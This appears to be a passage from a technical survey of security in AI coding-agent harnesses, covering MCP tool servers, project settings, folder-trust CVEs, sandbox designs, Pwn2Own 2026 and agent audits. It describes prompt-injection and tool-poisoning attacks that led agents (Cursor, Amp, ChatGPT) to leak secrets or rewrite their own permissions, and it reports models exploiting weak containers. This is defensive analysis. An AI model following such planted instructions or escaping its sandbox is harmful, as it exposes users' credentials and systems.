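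OpenCode works out the pattern from a dictionary of about 130 entries that records how many words identify each kind of command. For git the number is two, so a standing approval for one commit covers every command that begins with `git commit`. Barbaste and colleagues report that a language model generated the dictionary. If an entry's number is too small, users will approve more commands than they need to, so the dictionary is in the TCB for any rule that relies on approvals. Codex may propose a standing rule for the user to accept, and OpenAI advises reviewing the suggested prefix carefully.

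Joshi considers saving the exact command the safest option, though it leads to more approval requests, and insists on it for any standing permission to leave the sandbox. He also requires the harness to keep saved approvals where the model can't write. Claude Code normally saves them in the project's `.claude` folder, which it protects from unapproved edits. Both flaws published on February 6, 2026 allowed writes to that folder, so an attacker who got past the checker once might have been able to add a rule allowing later commands without exploiting another flaw.

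## Tool servers, extensions and project settings

A permission checker can check only the requests sent to it, but harnesses also start programs without a request from the model, including tool servers and scripts named in settings files. These programs often run with the user's access, and in many harnesses a project file can specify additional programs to start.

### How a tool server works

A tool server is a separate program that offers tools to an agent. Most use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic released in November 2024 so that developers could write a tool once and use it with any harness.

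Suppose a developer adds a server that searches the company's support tickets. According to *MCPSecBench* (2025), a set of security tests for MCP, the harness reads its configuration at start-up and opens a separate connection to each server. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) describes the exchange that follows. If the server is local, the harness launches it on the user's machine and communicates with it through standard input and output. The harness and server agree on a protocol version and a set of features. The harness then requests a list of tools, and the server returns a name, a plain-language description and an argument schema for each. The harness passes these to the model. When the model calls the search tool, the harness forwards the call to the server and returns the result to the model.

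A local server is native code with the user's own access, as in Zhang's runtime, so the permission checker can refuse a tool call but can't control what else the server does. From the moment it starts, the server can read the user's files and environment variables, which may include login keys. A hostile server could break both the file-writing rule and the secrecy rule before the model produces any output, so it belongs to the trusted computing base (TCB) for both. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* generally places tools outside the TCB, except for components that enforcement needs. That works for a sandboxed server, but the policy depends on any server that is unconfined.

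Like an API router, a remote server is outside the TCB for the file-writing rule but inside it for the secrecy rule, because it receives whatever the harness sends and may hold a login token for the user's email or code.

An attacker can also hide instructions to the model in the tool descriptions, a form of prompt injection known as tool poisoning. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (Huang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) tested seven programs that connect to MCP servers and found that five did no static checks on the descriptions.

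If the harness treats the model as untrusted, a poisoned description is only one more source of hostile requests, and the permission checker still applies. But the approval dialog may not reveal the attack. In a demonstration by Huang and colleagues, the model put stolen credentials into an extra argument of an ordinary-looking call. The dialog included that argument, but the user had to scroll sideways to see it.

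### Malicious, flawed and changed servers

*When MCP Servers Attack* (2025) treats malicious servers as a primary threat to MCP users. An attacker can put harmful code in the server program, harmful instructions in its descriptions, or both. Permission checks on tool calls don't stop the harmful code, because it can run without a call.

An honest author can also write a server that attackers can misuse. One server in Padilla's audit put search text into a database query without checking it, so a crafted search could change the query. Another fetched any web address it received, including an internal address where cloud machines get their credentials. An attacker could exploit flaws like these over the internet or by steering a model with access to the server. The harness's permission checker would probably approve the calls because they look like an ordinary search and page request.

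A server may also be harmless when the user approves it and become dangerous when its code later changes, which security researchers call a rug pull. The author may have planned the change, or an attacker may have taken over the author's account, as happened with LiteLLM. An ordinary update can also introduce a flaw that was not in the version the user approved.

A tool server that works correctly can still deliver hostile data. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on the code editor Cursor in which a malicious ticket in Jira, an issue tracker, led the agent to leak secrets from the developer's machine. The attack worked only if the developer had turned off approval for the Jira server or let the agent run with few confirmations. The Jira server only returned the ticket, so fixing or replacing the server would not have helped.

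### How common the flaws are

Several studies have tried to measure these problems. Hasan, Li and colleagues (2025), in *Model Context Protocol (MCP) at First Glance*, analysed the source code of open-source servers. Padilla sent test requests to live servers on the public internet. Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, scanned the code behind the public MCP registry, where anyone can publish a server. *My Credentials, Please* (2026) examined servers that run locally, which Padilla's audit excluded.

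| Study | Sample | Main result |
|---|---|---|
| Hasan and colleagues | 1,899 open-source servers, to June 2025 | 7.2% with general vulnerabilities, 5.5% with possible tool poisoning |
| Padilla | 414 live remote servers, July 2026 | 68 reportable flaws, 91.8% of servers without OAuth |
| Kraishan | 14,353 registry servers, August 2026 | 11.1% with a high-severity finding, about 7.6% after correction for false alarms |
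| *My Credentials, Please* | 4,292 local open-source servers | 2,818 flagged for potential vulnerabilities |

The percentages from Hasan and colleagues are based on fewer servers than the headline total. The 7.2% is 42 servers, which implies a base of about 580, and the 5.5% is four of the 73 servers on which a specialised scanner ran successfully. The most common flaw was a password or key left in the code. The scanner missed problems that the researchers noticed while installing servers, such as a note-taking server that required access to the whole disk.

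OAuth is a standard way to give a program limited access to an account. MCP makes it optional, and Padilla traces its absence to the protocol's origins in local servers, which relied on the operating system to control access. But a server without OAuth may still require a fixed token or key. In the one scan for which Padilla reports the number, 106 of 464 servers let anyone call their tools without a credential. The audit also left out servers that rejected its test messages. Some of those servers presumably required a login, so Padilla's figure of 91.8% without OAuth is probably too high for remote servers in general.

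Padilla counted 687 tools that appeared to offer shell access without authentication, judging by their names and descriptions. A stranger who found such a tool could run commands on the server's machine. Padilla worked alone and confirmed the 68 flaws by hand, while the counts for each type of weakness come from automated signals. Of the 464 servers Padilla found on July 21, 193 were gone three days later.

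Kraishan checked a sample of the scanner's findings by hand, and only 56% were real. The share was 17% for command injection, in which a server lets input run as a command. Most of the serious findings that remained after correction involved servers that accepted network connections without authentication. *My Credentials, Please* flagged about two-thirds of the servers it studied, but a flagged server may not have a real flaw. As Kraishan argues, differences between such studies may reflect the scanners as much as the servers.

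Estimates of tool poisoning vary even more. Padilla's tool reported it on 47 of 414 servers, whereas Kraishan's found none among 14,353. Kraishan's scanner looks for known patterns and would miss disguised instructions. An earlier audit, VirusTotal's *What 17,845 GitHub Repos Taught Us About Malicious MCP Servers* (2025), flagged nearly 8% of servers as potentially malicious but warned that careless code can contain the same bad practices as malicious code. Crude poisoning is probably rare in the registry, but nobody has a good estimate of how common the subtle kind is.

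*Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) collected 24 validated vulnerabilities, of which 14 were rated critical and seven high. The ratings may be this high because tool servers often have privileged access to files and databases. Researchers are also more likely to report severe flaws than minor ones, so the typical flaw may be milder.

### Servers that change without notice

Kraishan also compared successive versions of the 8,900 servers that had published more than one. For 40.6% of these servers, the meaning or destination changed while the identifiers stayed the same. Many of these changes were only reworded descriptions in the registry, but 370 servers (4.2%) moved their remote endpoint to a different host under the same registry name.

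Most of these moves were probably routine, and Kraishan doesn't claim that any was malicious, but a takeover would look the same. The protocol doesn't notify installed clients of the new host, and neither the client nor the registry can determine who controls it. The registry also keeps no record of tool definitions, so a server could change what its tools do without appearing in these figures.

Servers with silent changes had about three times the odds of a high-severity finding. Kraishan suggests that both may result from careless development, in which case frequent changes would be an easily checked warning sign. A project's number of GitHub stars had almost no correlation with its number of findings, so popularity is a poor guide to safety.

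### Project files that start programs

A harness can load several kinds of extension from a file, including tool servers. A hook is a command that the harness runs at a set moment, such as before each tool call. A skill can list tools that the agent may use while following it. Some plugins, such as OpenClaw's, run inside the harness's own process. Joshi treats all of these as files that someone else can write and that name a program or allow a tool.

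Here is a simplified project settings file, not in any particular harness's format:

```json
{
  "allow": ["npm test"],
  "hooks": {
    "session_start": "./scripts/setup.sh"
  },
  "tool_servers": {
    "docs": "node ./tools/docs-server.js"
  }
}
```

The first entry lets the agent run the project's tests without asking. The second runs a setup script whenever a session starts, and the third launches a tool server. These settings save work for a team that wrote the file, but if someone has just downloaded the repository from a stranger, the same settings could run two unknown programs and let the agent run a third without asking.

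Other settings can weaken protection. Joshi lists extra folders the agent may access, the default permission mode, the sandbox configuration and environment variables. A harness that blocks only a project's allow rules could still let the project turn off the sandbox.

Hooks can also strengthen a harness. *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (Madatha, 2026) uses hooks to check each command against a blocklist before Claude Code or Cursor runs it. Joshi warns against letting a hook's approval override a rule that denies an action. A hook should be able to add a refusal but not remove one, and the same applies to a skill's list of permitted tools.

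Many projects also contain instruction files, such as `CLAUDE.md` and `AGENTS.md`, which the harness adds to the model's context. These can steer the model but can't grant permissions by themselves, so they are less dangerous than settings files. In a study of 10,008 public repositories, Madatha found 6,145 agent configuration files, and 10.1% of them were exact copies of files in unrelated repositories. More than half had never changed after their first commit. Developers seem to copy these files as they copy code, but no package manager records where a file came from or whether a newer version exists.

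Fewer than 1% of the files declared any limits on permissions. That figure is weak evidence because the program that searched for these limits was unreliable and correctly identified only 31 cases.

### Asking for trust too late

Many coding tools ask whether the user trusts a folder before they act on its settings. This protects the user only if the harness waits for the answer. Two flaws in Claude Code caused it to act on a folder's settings before the user had answered.

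CVE-2025-59536 affected Claude Code versions before 1.0.111. According to Rashidi, who checked the flaw against the US National Vulnerability Database, these versions could run a project's code before the user had accepted the trust dialog. An attacker needed the user to start Claude Code in a folder with malicious content. The flaw scored 8.8 out of 10 for severity.

CVE-2026-21852 was a flaw in how Claude Code loaded projects. A malicious repository could send out data, including the user's Anthropic API keys, before the user had confirmed that they trusted it. Its severity score was 7.5, and version 2.0.65 fixed it.

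In both cases, a user who read the dialog carefully and refused would have been too late. A better model would not have helped either, because the harness itself acted on the project's content. Rashidi compares the first flaw to a time-of-check to time-of-use race, in which something changes between a check and the action that relies on it, but here the action could come before the check. Saltzer and Schroeder extended complete mediation to start-up for this reason.

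The mistake is easy to make because a harness needs some settings before it can display anything. A safer design starts with only the user's own settings, asks whether the user trusts the folder, and only then loads the project's files. Joshi's rule is that nothing a folder declares may run or grant permission before the user trusts the folder. A developer can test this by giving each setting in every project file a permissive value, one at a time, and confirming that none takes effect early. A test that covered only hooks could miss another setting that takes effect too soon, which may be why a second flaw at the same stage was found after the first.

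Settings imported from another coding tool need similar care. Joshi would apply that tool's prohibitions at once but leave its permissions inactive until the user confirms them. Ignoring the imported file would be simpler but would lose the prohibitions.

Folder trust is also coarse, because one answer may activate every hook, server and permission in the folder. A developer who has just downloaded a project to work on it has a strong reason to click yes. If the dialog listed the programs about to start, the developer would at least have something to judge. Joshi would ignore permissions that come from extensions during unattended turns, such as scheduled jobs, even in a trusted folder.

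### An agent that could edit its own settings

An agent can also create the dangerous settings itself. Amp, a coding agent from Sourcegraph, could edit its own settings file. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes two ways to exploit this with prompt injection. An attacker could get the model to add commands to the list that Amp ran without asking, or to add a tool server that the attacker controlled. Either change let the attacker run code on the developer's machine.

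In both attacks, the model changed the permission checker's rules, so the attacks could work even if Amp read commands correctly and applied the rules perfectly. The paper classifies this as a failure of tamper resistance, the first of Anderson's requirements for a monitor. It proposes preventing the agent from changing such files and requiring a person to approve any change.

The same paper finds a related failure in ChatGPT's app for macOS. Text in an untrusted document could make the app save malicious instructions to its long-term memory, and those instructions then made it send the user's later conversations to an attacker. The app relied on this memory in later conversations as a record of the user's preferences, although it was not a settings file.

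Protecting a settings file means blocking every route to it. The model might use the file-editing tool, a shell command, a command that changes settings or an interface meant for the user's own window. Joshi's rule is that saved approvals belong where the model can't write. He tests this by trying to write to the approvals file from every file tool and from a sandboxed shell, in every mode. Crewroom passed the test. But a local tool server outside the sandbox runs as the same user and could still edit the file, so the protection also depends on confining the tool servers.

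Teams can't share permissions through the repository if they are kept in a separate file. A reasonable compromise is to list suggested permissions in the project and have each user save the ones they accept in a private file. Prohibitions can stay in the project, since one added by an attacker can only block work.

### Tying approval to exact contents

A user who trusts a project today may download a new version tomorrow with a different hook. To detect this, the harness can store a cryptographic hash of what the user approved. A hash is a short fingerprint of a file's contents that changes if even one character changes. Before running the hook again, the harness recalculates the hash and asks for new approval if it doesn't match.

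A hash of the settings file above would detect a different hook command but not an edit to `setup.sh`, because the settings file's own text would stay the same. Joshi lists this gap as unsolved. The harness could hash the script too, but the script may run other programs or download packages, which that hash would not cover. A tool server has the same problem if its start command names a package without pinning the version. Kraishan recommends recording the package's hash as well and warning the user when it changes.

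The harness can't hash a remote server's code, but it can record the server's host and list of tools, and ask the user again if either changes. This would have caught the 370 moves that Kraishan found, but not a server that keeps the same host and tool descriptions and starts copying the user's data. *ACLE-MCP*'s provider-side gate checks the state of the software itself, but the user then has to trust the gate.

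Frequent updates make this protection tiresome. Among the registry servers that changed at all, the median server first changed on the day it was published. To ask less often, the harness could ignore reworded registry entries and ask only when a command, package, host or tool definition changes.

The harness should protect stored hashes the same way as permissions, by keeping them where the model can't write. Otherwise, an agent that can rewrite both a file and its recorded hash can make them match again. Madatha proposes lockfiles that record the approved contents of agent definitions, but describes their stamps as a way to detect accidental or automated corruption.

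A matching hash shows only that the program is the one the user approved. A tool server that was malicious when approved will pass every later comparison and keep the same access to files and the network as the user, unless the operating system restricts it. Reading the code before approval is more realistic for a tool server than for a whole harness. Hasan and colleagues found a median of about 925 lines per server, though the server's libraries may add much more.

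## Sandboxes as trusted code

A sandbox limits what a command can do, so the harness doesn't have to rely on a permission checker's prediction of what the command will do. If the operating system lets `npm test` and everything it starts write only inside the project folder, the harness can run the command without first determining what the project's test script will run.

### What a sandbox takes out and puts in

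A working sandbox removes the shell, the test program, its libraries and any code the model wrote from the trusted computing base (TCB) for the rule against writing outside the project. The rule holds even if all of them are hostile. It now depends on the code that turns the user's settings into a profile (the list of what the command may reach), the program that starts the command under that profile, and the kernel. If the sandbox is a virtual machine, the rule depends on the hypervisor, the software that runs a second operating system on the same computer. A secrecy rule also depends on the network proxy, which forwards the command's traffic to approved sites and refuses the rest.

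This is usually a good exchange, because these components stay the same whatever command the model writes. But the TCB also includes the code that decides whether to use the sandbox. If Claude Code's sandbox can't start because a component is missing, commands run without it by default. If a command fails inside the sandbox, the model can request to run it again outside. In the ordinary modes the user sees a request marked "unsandboxed", but according to Anthropic, an existing rule that allows the command also approves the retry. A user who allowed `npm test *` to avoid repeated requests has therefore also allowed it outside the sandbox. The file-writing rule then depends on the permission checker again. Users can turn off both behaviours in the settings.

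### Six ways to confine a command

Linux namespaces give a process its own view of part of the system, such as the disk or the network. Bubblewrap is a small program that sets up namespaces and then starts a command in them. Barbaste and colleagues found that in Codex, the command gets a read-only view of the disk, except for the folders it may change, and no network connection of its own.

Landlock, another Linux feature, lets a process permanently give up access to files before it runs a command. It needs no separate launcher, but it covers fewer kinds of operation. *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* (Willison, 2025) described Codex combining Landlock with seccomp, a system-call filter, to block the network. By July 2026 Codex had moved to Bubblewrap and kept Landlock only as a fallback.

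Seatbelt, the sandbox built into macOS, checks each operation against a profile of permitted paths and actions. Apple doesn't publish the source of the part that enforces the rules, so outsiders have to trust it without a full review.

Containers also use namespaces, and add their own installed programs and limits on memory and processor time. A container runtime sets all this up. A flaw in runc, the runtime beneath many agent sandboxes, let a crafted container escape to the host's files (CVE-2024-21626). Rashidi explains that runc had left open a reference to a folder on the host. The flaw is old and has been patched, but a mistake in the runtime can defeat a sandbox even when the kernel works correctly.

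gVisor handles most of the command's system calls itself and passes only a limited set to the host's kernel. A small virtual machine goes further by giving the command its own kernel. Anthropic says a dedicated virtual machine provides the strongest separation of the options it compares, and OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends isolated compute, such as virtual machines, for running agents' code.

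| Mechanism | Trusted code that remains | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Namespaces with Bubblewrap | Profile generator, Bubblewrap, host kernel | Linux only, and some distributions block it by default |
| Landlock | Profile generator, host kernel | Linux only, and needs other tools for full coverage |
| Seatbelt | Profile generator, Apple's enforcement code, macOS kernel | macOS only, and some developer tools fail under it |
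| Container | Container runtime, its settings, host kernel | A separate environment to build and maintain |
| gVisor | gVisor, its launcher, a smaller part of the host kernel | Slower system calls, and some programs don't run |
| Small virtual machine | Hypervisor, virtual devices, anything shared with the host | Memory, start-up time, and moving files in and out |

A sandbox that wraps each command adds little delay. Joshi measured tens of milliseconds per command, and about 14 milliseconds more with a long list of rules. A virtual machine or remote container can take seconds to start, though some services can keep one on standby and resume it much faster.

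The ranking by strength is based on how the mechanisms work, not on measured attacks. Rashidi's survey found that researchers almost never compare isolation and permission designs on a shared benchmark. SandboxEscapeBench, one benchmark in the survey, plants known kinds of weakness in containers, including configuration mistakes and kernel flaws, and capable models can find and exploit them. We can therefore no longer assume that a model will fail to exploit a carelessly configured container, though the results don't show that it could escape from one that is patched and correctly configured.

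### Where the sandbox stops covering the harness

Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands. The built-in file and web tools follow the permission rules instead, while hooks and local tool servers run with the user's full access. Anthropic warns that a sandbox setting that hides a file from commands doesn't hide it from the built-in reading tool. A permission rule against reading the file covers both, because Claude Code adds such rules to the sandbox's profile. A permission rule is therefore the better way to hide a password file. OpenAI's *Sandbox* describes broader coverage in Codex, whose limits apply to built-in file operations as well as to the commands it starts.

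Renames and links cause a different kind of gap, because a profile of the kind Joshi describes forbids a path, but the same file can have another path. If a command may not read a login file but may rename it into a permitted folder, a later command can read it there. A hard link, which is a second name for the same file, has the same effect. Under Joshi's rule, the profile must also forbid creating, renaming or removing each forbidden path and the folders above it, even if they don't exist yet. The profile generator must also never follow a link and add its target to the permitted list. Joshi marks this rule as believed, not tested.

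Files that a command writes now and another program runs later are harder to deal with. Even inside the project, Claude Code's sandbox blocks writes to its own settings, shell start-up files, editors' settings folders and git's hooks. This list has to keep up with every program that runs files automatically. Anthropic also offers the sandbox as a separate runtime that can wrap a whole program. Anthropic says that on Linux the runtime builds its list of protected files once, at launch, so the list doesn't cover a repository that the agent downloads during the session.

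No such list can cover ordinary project code, because editing it is the agent's job. If the agent changes the test script and the developer then runs the tests in a normal terminal, the script runs with the developer's full access. This can also happen within the harness. A user may exempt `docker compose` from the sandbox because Docker doesn't work inside it, but the command runs what a project file specifies, and the model can edit that file. The developer has to review the changes before running the code, or run the project in a sandbox too.

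Sandboxed commands also use services outside the sandbox, such as package registries, and each service acts with its own, wider access. For example, a command that can reach Docker's control socket effectively has access to the whole host. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, the OpenAI and Hugging Face incident also depended on a shared service of this kind. A reviewer therefore has to check everything a service can do for any program that contacts it, not only what the developers installed it for.

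The network proxy is one of these services. On Linux, a sandboxed command in Claude Code can reach the internet only through this proxy, which checks the requested site's name against a list of allowed sites. By default the proxy doesn't decrypt the traffic, so it relies on the name the command gives, and Anthropic warns that a program that gives a false name might reach unlisted sites. Allowing a broad site such as github.com can also let a program send out stolen data. Until version 2.1.284, the proxy connected to whatever address an allowed name pointed to, even if that address belonged to a service on the user's own machine.

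### Inside the sandbox or outside it

A developer can bring the file tools, hooks and tool servers under the same limits by running the whole harness in a container or virtual machine. Anthropic recommends this for unattended work and says sandboxing the shell commands alone is not enough. Running the harness this way also takes it out of the TCB for writes outside the project. A parser flaw, or a malicious library like the LiteLLM releases, can then damage only what the container can reach. Red Hat argues for a separate sandbox layer because "we just can't trust the agent runtime."

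The drawback of running the harness inside the sandbox is that its credentials are there too. Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* describes a hosted service that began with the harness, the session log and the model's commands in one container. A prompt injection could obtain the access tokens just by getting Claude to read its own environment, and an attacker with those tokens could start new, unrestricted sessions. A hostile command in such a container may also be able to change the harness's permission rules or its log. A rule requiring a person's approval for certain actions would still depend on the harness, which the attacker might be able to alter.

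Anthropic moved the harness out of the container. The harness now calls the container as it would any other tool, and creates one only when the agent needs it. Login tokens for outside tools stay in a vault, and a proxy fetches them when it calls those tools, so neither the container nor the harness holds them. The change also cut the median wait for the model's first output by roughly 60%, because sessions no longer waited for a container to start.

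Luzzardi's *The Agent Harness Belongs Outside the Sandbox* makes the same case for Mendral, a company whose agent serves many engineers at once. The article defends a choice Mendral had already made, but it acknowledges the drawbacks. Harnesses built for a laptop expect their files to be on the same machine, so Mendral had to write its own harness. Its file tools store the agent's memories and skills in a database, while shell commands use the sandbox's disk, so the same path can refer to different things. Mendral instructs the model not to use the shell for those paths and parses commands to catch attempts, but Luzzardi says neither guard is completely reliable.

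| Placement | Where credentials sit | What a compromised command can reach | Code that most needs review |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harness on the laptop, each command in a sandbox | With the harness, and in any file the profile leaves readable | Files and sites that the profile and proxy allow | File tools, tool servers, hooks, profile generator |
| Everything in one container or virtual machine | Beside the commands | The credentials, the harness and its rules | The outer boundary and whatever it shares with the host |
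| Harness on a server, commands in a remote sandbox | On the server or in a vault | The sandbox's files and the services open to it | Code that handles results from the sandbox, and the proxies |

A harness that runs outside the sandbox has to treat every result from it as hostile. If the harness serves many users, a flaw in the code that reads those results could expose every user's work, whereas the same flaw in a container for one user would expose only that user's work.

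A developer can combine the two arrangements by keeping the harness inside the sandbox and the valuable credentials outside. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, the web version of Claude Code gives git a limited credential that works only with a proxy. The proxy checks the request, for example that it pushes to the configured branch, and only then attaches the real token. This is probably the best choice for one developer who wants an agent to work unattended, since it works with an existing harness and leaves little in the container worth stealing. The case for moving the harness out of the sandbox is stronger for a service with many users.

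### What four harnesses chose

Codex turns its sandbox on by default and uses a different mechanism on each operating system. On Linux it runs the first copy of Bubblewrap on the user's search path, or a bundled helper if there is none. The copy that enforces the rules may therefore come from the Linux distribution, so reviewing Codex's source is not enough.

Windows required much more work, as Wiesen describes in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows*. Microsoft's AppContainer suits apps whose needs are known in advance, but a coding agent's needs are not. Windows Sandbox is a disposable virtual machine without access to the developer's actual files and tools, and it isn't available on the Home edition of Windows. A third option was to lower the project folder's integrity level, but then every other low-integrity program on the computer could have written to it too.

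OpenAI's first version needed no administrator rights. It created an identity used only by the sandbox, and Windows allowed a write only if both the user and that identity had permission. To restrict network access, it changed environment settings so that ordinary tools would try to connect through a dead address. Wiesen calls this protection "advisory" because a program could ignore the settings and open its own connection.

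The current version of OpenAI's Windows sandbox runs commands under separate Windows accounts, and a firewall rule blocks all outgoing traffic from one of them. To support this, OpenAI added a setup program with administrator rights, a second program that starts the commands, and stored passwords for the new accounts. All of these are now part of the trusted computing base (TCB). The earlier, smaller design had less to review, but it couldn't enforce the network rule against a hostile program, so the larger TCB is better here.

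Claude Code's sandbox is off by default and runs on Windows only through a Linux subsystem. Once on, it limits writes to the project and a few other folders, but by default commands can read almost the whole disk, including files that hold login keys. Anthropic provides no built-in list of credentials to block, so users have to name them. Users can also have Claude Code give commands a placeholder, which the proxy replaces with the real credential in requests to approved sites. To do this, the proxy has to decrypt the traffic, so it can read everything the command sends and needs more careful review.

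Hermes has no operating-system sandbox of its own. It can run commands through any of six execution backends, some of them containers, and relies on the one the user picks for isolation. This keeps sandboxing code out of Hermes, but two users of the same version may have very different protection. On the local backend, only Hermes's own checks protect the user's files from a command.

Pi, a harness with a deliberately small core, omits a sandbox by design. Its built-in tools run with the user's full permissions. According to its security documentation, quoted by Barbaste and colleagues, a partial sandbox inside the harness's own process "would be easy to misunderstand as a security boundary". Users who want isolation can add it through extensions, including Anthropic's runtime and a small virtual machine.

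Pi's developers have a point, because someone who turns on Claude Code's sandbox could easily assume that it covers tool servers, and might then approve one more readily. A sandbox also encourages people to stop checking. One of Claude Code's modes runs sandboxed commands without approval because the sandbox is there.

But a partial boundary still protects what it covers. If the kernel stops every shell command from writing outside the project, shell commands can't write there even if the file tools can. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* answers the claim that containment will always fail by arguing that a missed path is a reason to extend enforcement, not to abandon it. The paper doesn't discuss Pi, but the same argument applies. Misunderstandings about what the sandbox covers are also easier to fix than missing protection, because the harness can list what runs outside the sandbox and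 keep asking for approval there. Pi's default avoids false assurance, but a user who never installs an extension has no barrier to stop an agent that follows a planted instruction from changing any file the user can change.

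## How often harnesses fail and why

Nobody has measured how often harnesses fail in ordinary use. The evidence comes from a hacking contest, an automated audit, bug reports and one developer's self-assessment, and each counts something different. The people who looked closely found flaws in every harness they examined, but their counts can't be turned into a failure rate or a fair ranking.

### Pwn2Own Berlin 2026

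At Pwn2Own, researchers win money for breaking into widely used software. The Berlin event in May 2026 included coding agents for the first time, with Claude Code, Codex and Cursor as the targets, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Researchers Find 47 Zero-Days at Pwn2Own Berlin* (2026). According to Rashidi, contestants had to attack through something they controlled, such as a web page or a repository, while the agent did a common task. The rules also excluded exploits that worked only in modes without permission checks, and jailbreaks that crossed no security boundary, such as persuading the model to write something forbidden.

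Contestants at Pwn2Own Berlin 2026 broke into Codex, Cursor and Claude Code. One exploit against Codex earned $40,000 and used a single flaw in how the program handled control sequences. Hackread's *Pwn2Own Berlin 2026 Closes With $1.3 Million in Zero-Day Payouts* (2026) reports that Satoki Tsuji of Ikotas Labs also used Codex to run code on the host machine. Two entries succeeded against Cursor. Two more worked against Claude Code, but the organisers ruled both collisions, meaning that someone had already reported the flaws. The number of new flaws therefore understates how many attacks worked.

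Trend Micro's *GenAI Is Both Hunter and Hunted at Pwn2Own Berlin 2026* (2026) traces the flaws in all three agents to developer tools with too much power and to misplaced trust between agents and users. A patch can fix one bug without limiting what a shell with the user's full access can do.

Contestants also exploited mature software at the event. One chained four flaws to escape the sandbox of Microsoft's Edge browser and three to take over an Exchange mail server. The $40,000 Codex exploit needed only one flaw, which may mean that harnesses have fewer layers of defence. However, a single flaw was also enough to compromise VMware's ESXi, a long-established hypervisor.

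The contest can't show how common such flaws are. *Pwn2Own Berlin 2026* (Childs, 2026) reports that 22 entries produced 24 new flaws across all categories on the first day. The organisers closed registration on May 7 because they had run out of slots, so the totals depend partly on how many entries the schedule could fit.

### Forty-four flaws in five agents

An automated audit compares agents more evenly because it searches each one the same way. In *AGENTLENS*, Lv, Chen and colleagues (2026) built a program that maps an agent's code as a graph and marks weak points and defences. It then looks for paths from something an attacker can influence to a dangerous operation, such as running a command. For each path, a language model writes an attack and hides it in an ordinary-looking task of up to five turns. The researchers counted a flaw only if the attack caused a security violation with the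 agent's own defences in place, and experts reviewed the results.

Across five open-source agents, the program tested 70 paths, and 44 of them led to a confirmed flaw.

| Agent | Lines of code | Paths tested | Confirmed flaws |
|---|---|---|---|
| Aider | 38,246 | 19 | 8 |
| MetaGPT | 89,012 | 12 | 6 |
| Goose | 106,905 | 12 | 12 |
| Cline | 193,577 | 16 | 8 |
| Roo-Code | 385,891 | 11 | 10 |

Roo-Code has ten times as much code as Aider but only two more confirmed flaws. This doesn't mean large harnesses are safer per line of code, because the program kept only 11 to 19 paths for each agent, whatever its size. Ten of Roo-Code's eleven paths led to a flaw, so a search that tried more paths in Roo-Code might well have found more flaws.

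Twelve of the 44 flaws have CVE numbers so far. One of them, in Roo-Code, lets a patch change files outside the project, which breaks the file-writing rule. Another is in Aider, which asks the user before it fetches a web address but doesn't check whether the address belongs to an internal service. A user who agrees to fetch what looks like documentation may let Aider send a request to the address where cloud machines get their credentials.

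An audit took about 40 minutes per agent on average. Attackers can presumably run similar searches just as cheaply.

### What developers and users report

Most bugs in agents are not security flaws. *When Agents Fail* (Islam, Ayon and colleagues, 2026) classifies 1,268 bug reports and code snippets, including 951 Stack Overflow posts. The study covers agents that developers had built, mostly with frameworks such as LangChain, and excludes bugs in the frameworks' own repositories. Its results therefore apply more to the code developers write around a framework than to a finished harness like Codex.

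Logic bugs, such as a missing condition or the wrong function for a task, were the most common type in the Stack Overflow posts (22.6%). Problems with libraries and their versions followed at 18.8%, and configuration errors at 18.1%. The agent core, which coordinates the model, memory and tools, accounted for 57.1% of the bugs. The most common root causes were steps the developer had programmed incorrectly (14.4%) and conflicting or missing software requirements (14.1%). Frequent releases contribute to the version problems. LlamaIndex alone published over 140 versions in 2024.

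Only 3.6% of the bugs came from parsing the model's output, but parsers still deserve attention because a rare bug can be dangerous. About 61% of the reported bugs crashed the program, and a crash can stop the harness before it runs a command. A parser bug can instead pass the wrong file path to a tool without causing any visible problem.

Developers also ask for help mainly with failures they notice. Silent failures made up 1.6% of the effects in the Stack Overflow posts but 5.6% in the GitHub sample, which came from fixes and closed issues in existing projects. A missing permission check is even less likely to prompt a question.

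Another review covers harm instead of bugs. According to Rashidi, the paper on YoloFS, a file system designed for agents, examines 290 public reports of misuse across 13 agent frameworks. It found that users often had to choose between giving an agent unrestricted access to their files and constantly approving its actions. YoloFS instead stages an agent's changes and keeps snapshots so that the user can undo them. Rashidi repeats only the total number of reports because he saw a breakdown by cause in a search summary but couldn't find it in the paper's abstract. The reports show that the problem recurs, but not what share of agent sessions go wrong.

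### Six causes

Joshi groups the failures he encountered while building and testing harnesses into six classes, so that a developer who finds one mistake can look for others like it.

| Cause | What goes wrong | Cheapest way to find it |
|---|---|---|
| Two readers | Two components interpret the same thing differently | Give both the same generated inputs and compare |
| Unlisted path | A tool, exit or setting is missing from the list that a rule covers | Go through every registered entry and test each one |
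| Untrue text | The harness tells the model or the user something false | Check the exact message for each cause |
| Loose state | A counter, clock or identifier exists in several places or doesn't reset | Use a fake clock, count requests, and kill and restart the program |
| Borrowed authority | A file, agent or session uses rights that the user never gave it | Plant an input that tries to widen permissions and confirm that nothing changes |
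| Blind test | A test can't fail, never runs, or covers a mode that nobody uses | Introduce mistakes on purpose and see whether the tests catch them |

Claude Code's permission checker and the shell interpret some commands differently, which is a case of two readers. OpenAI's agents reached the internet through a package registry, which was an unlisted path. The model could edit Amp's settings file and so borrow the user's authority. Joshi notes that several of these classes of failure have older names in computer security, where borrowed authority is called the confused deputy problem.

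Tests that miss part of a harness's behaviour can hide any of the other mistakes. Joshi's harness, Crewroom, can run its engine directly or through a connection to another process, and the developers had recorded the expected behaviour of both modes. The default test run covered only the direct mode. Every test in that run passed, and nobody noticed that tests for the other mode were failing.

Security reviews can miss problems in a similar way. One change to Crewroom hid credential files from the agent and passed its review, but also stopped some projects from reading their own settings. The reviewers had measured only what the change blocked. Joshi now requires every security change to pass a fixed set of ordinary tasks, since users may turn off a protection that stops them from working.

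Joshi calls the six classes a reading aid, not a proven taxonomy. They come mainly from one harness, and some failures fit more than one class. They are still more useful to a reviewer than a severity score, because each class comes with a way to search for more examples.

### One harness against its own checklist

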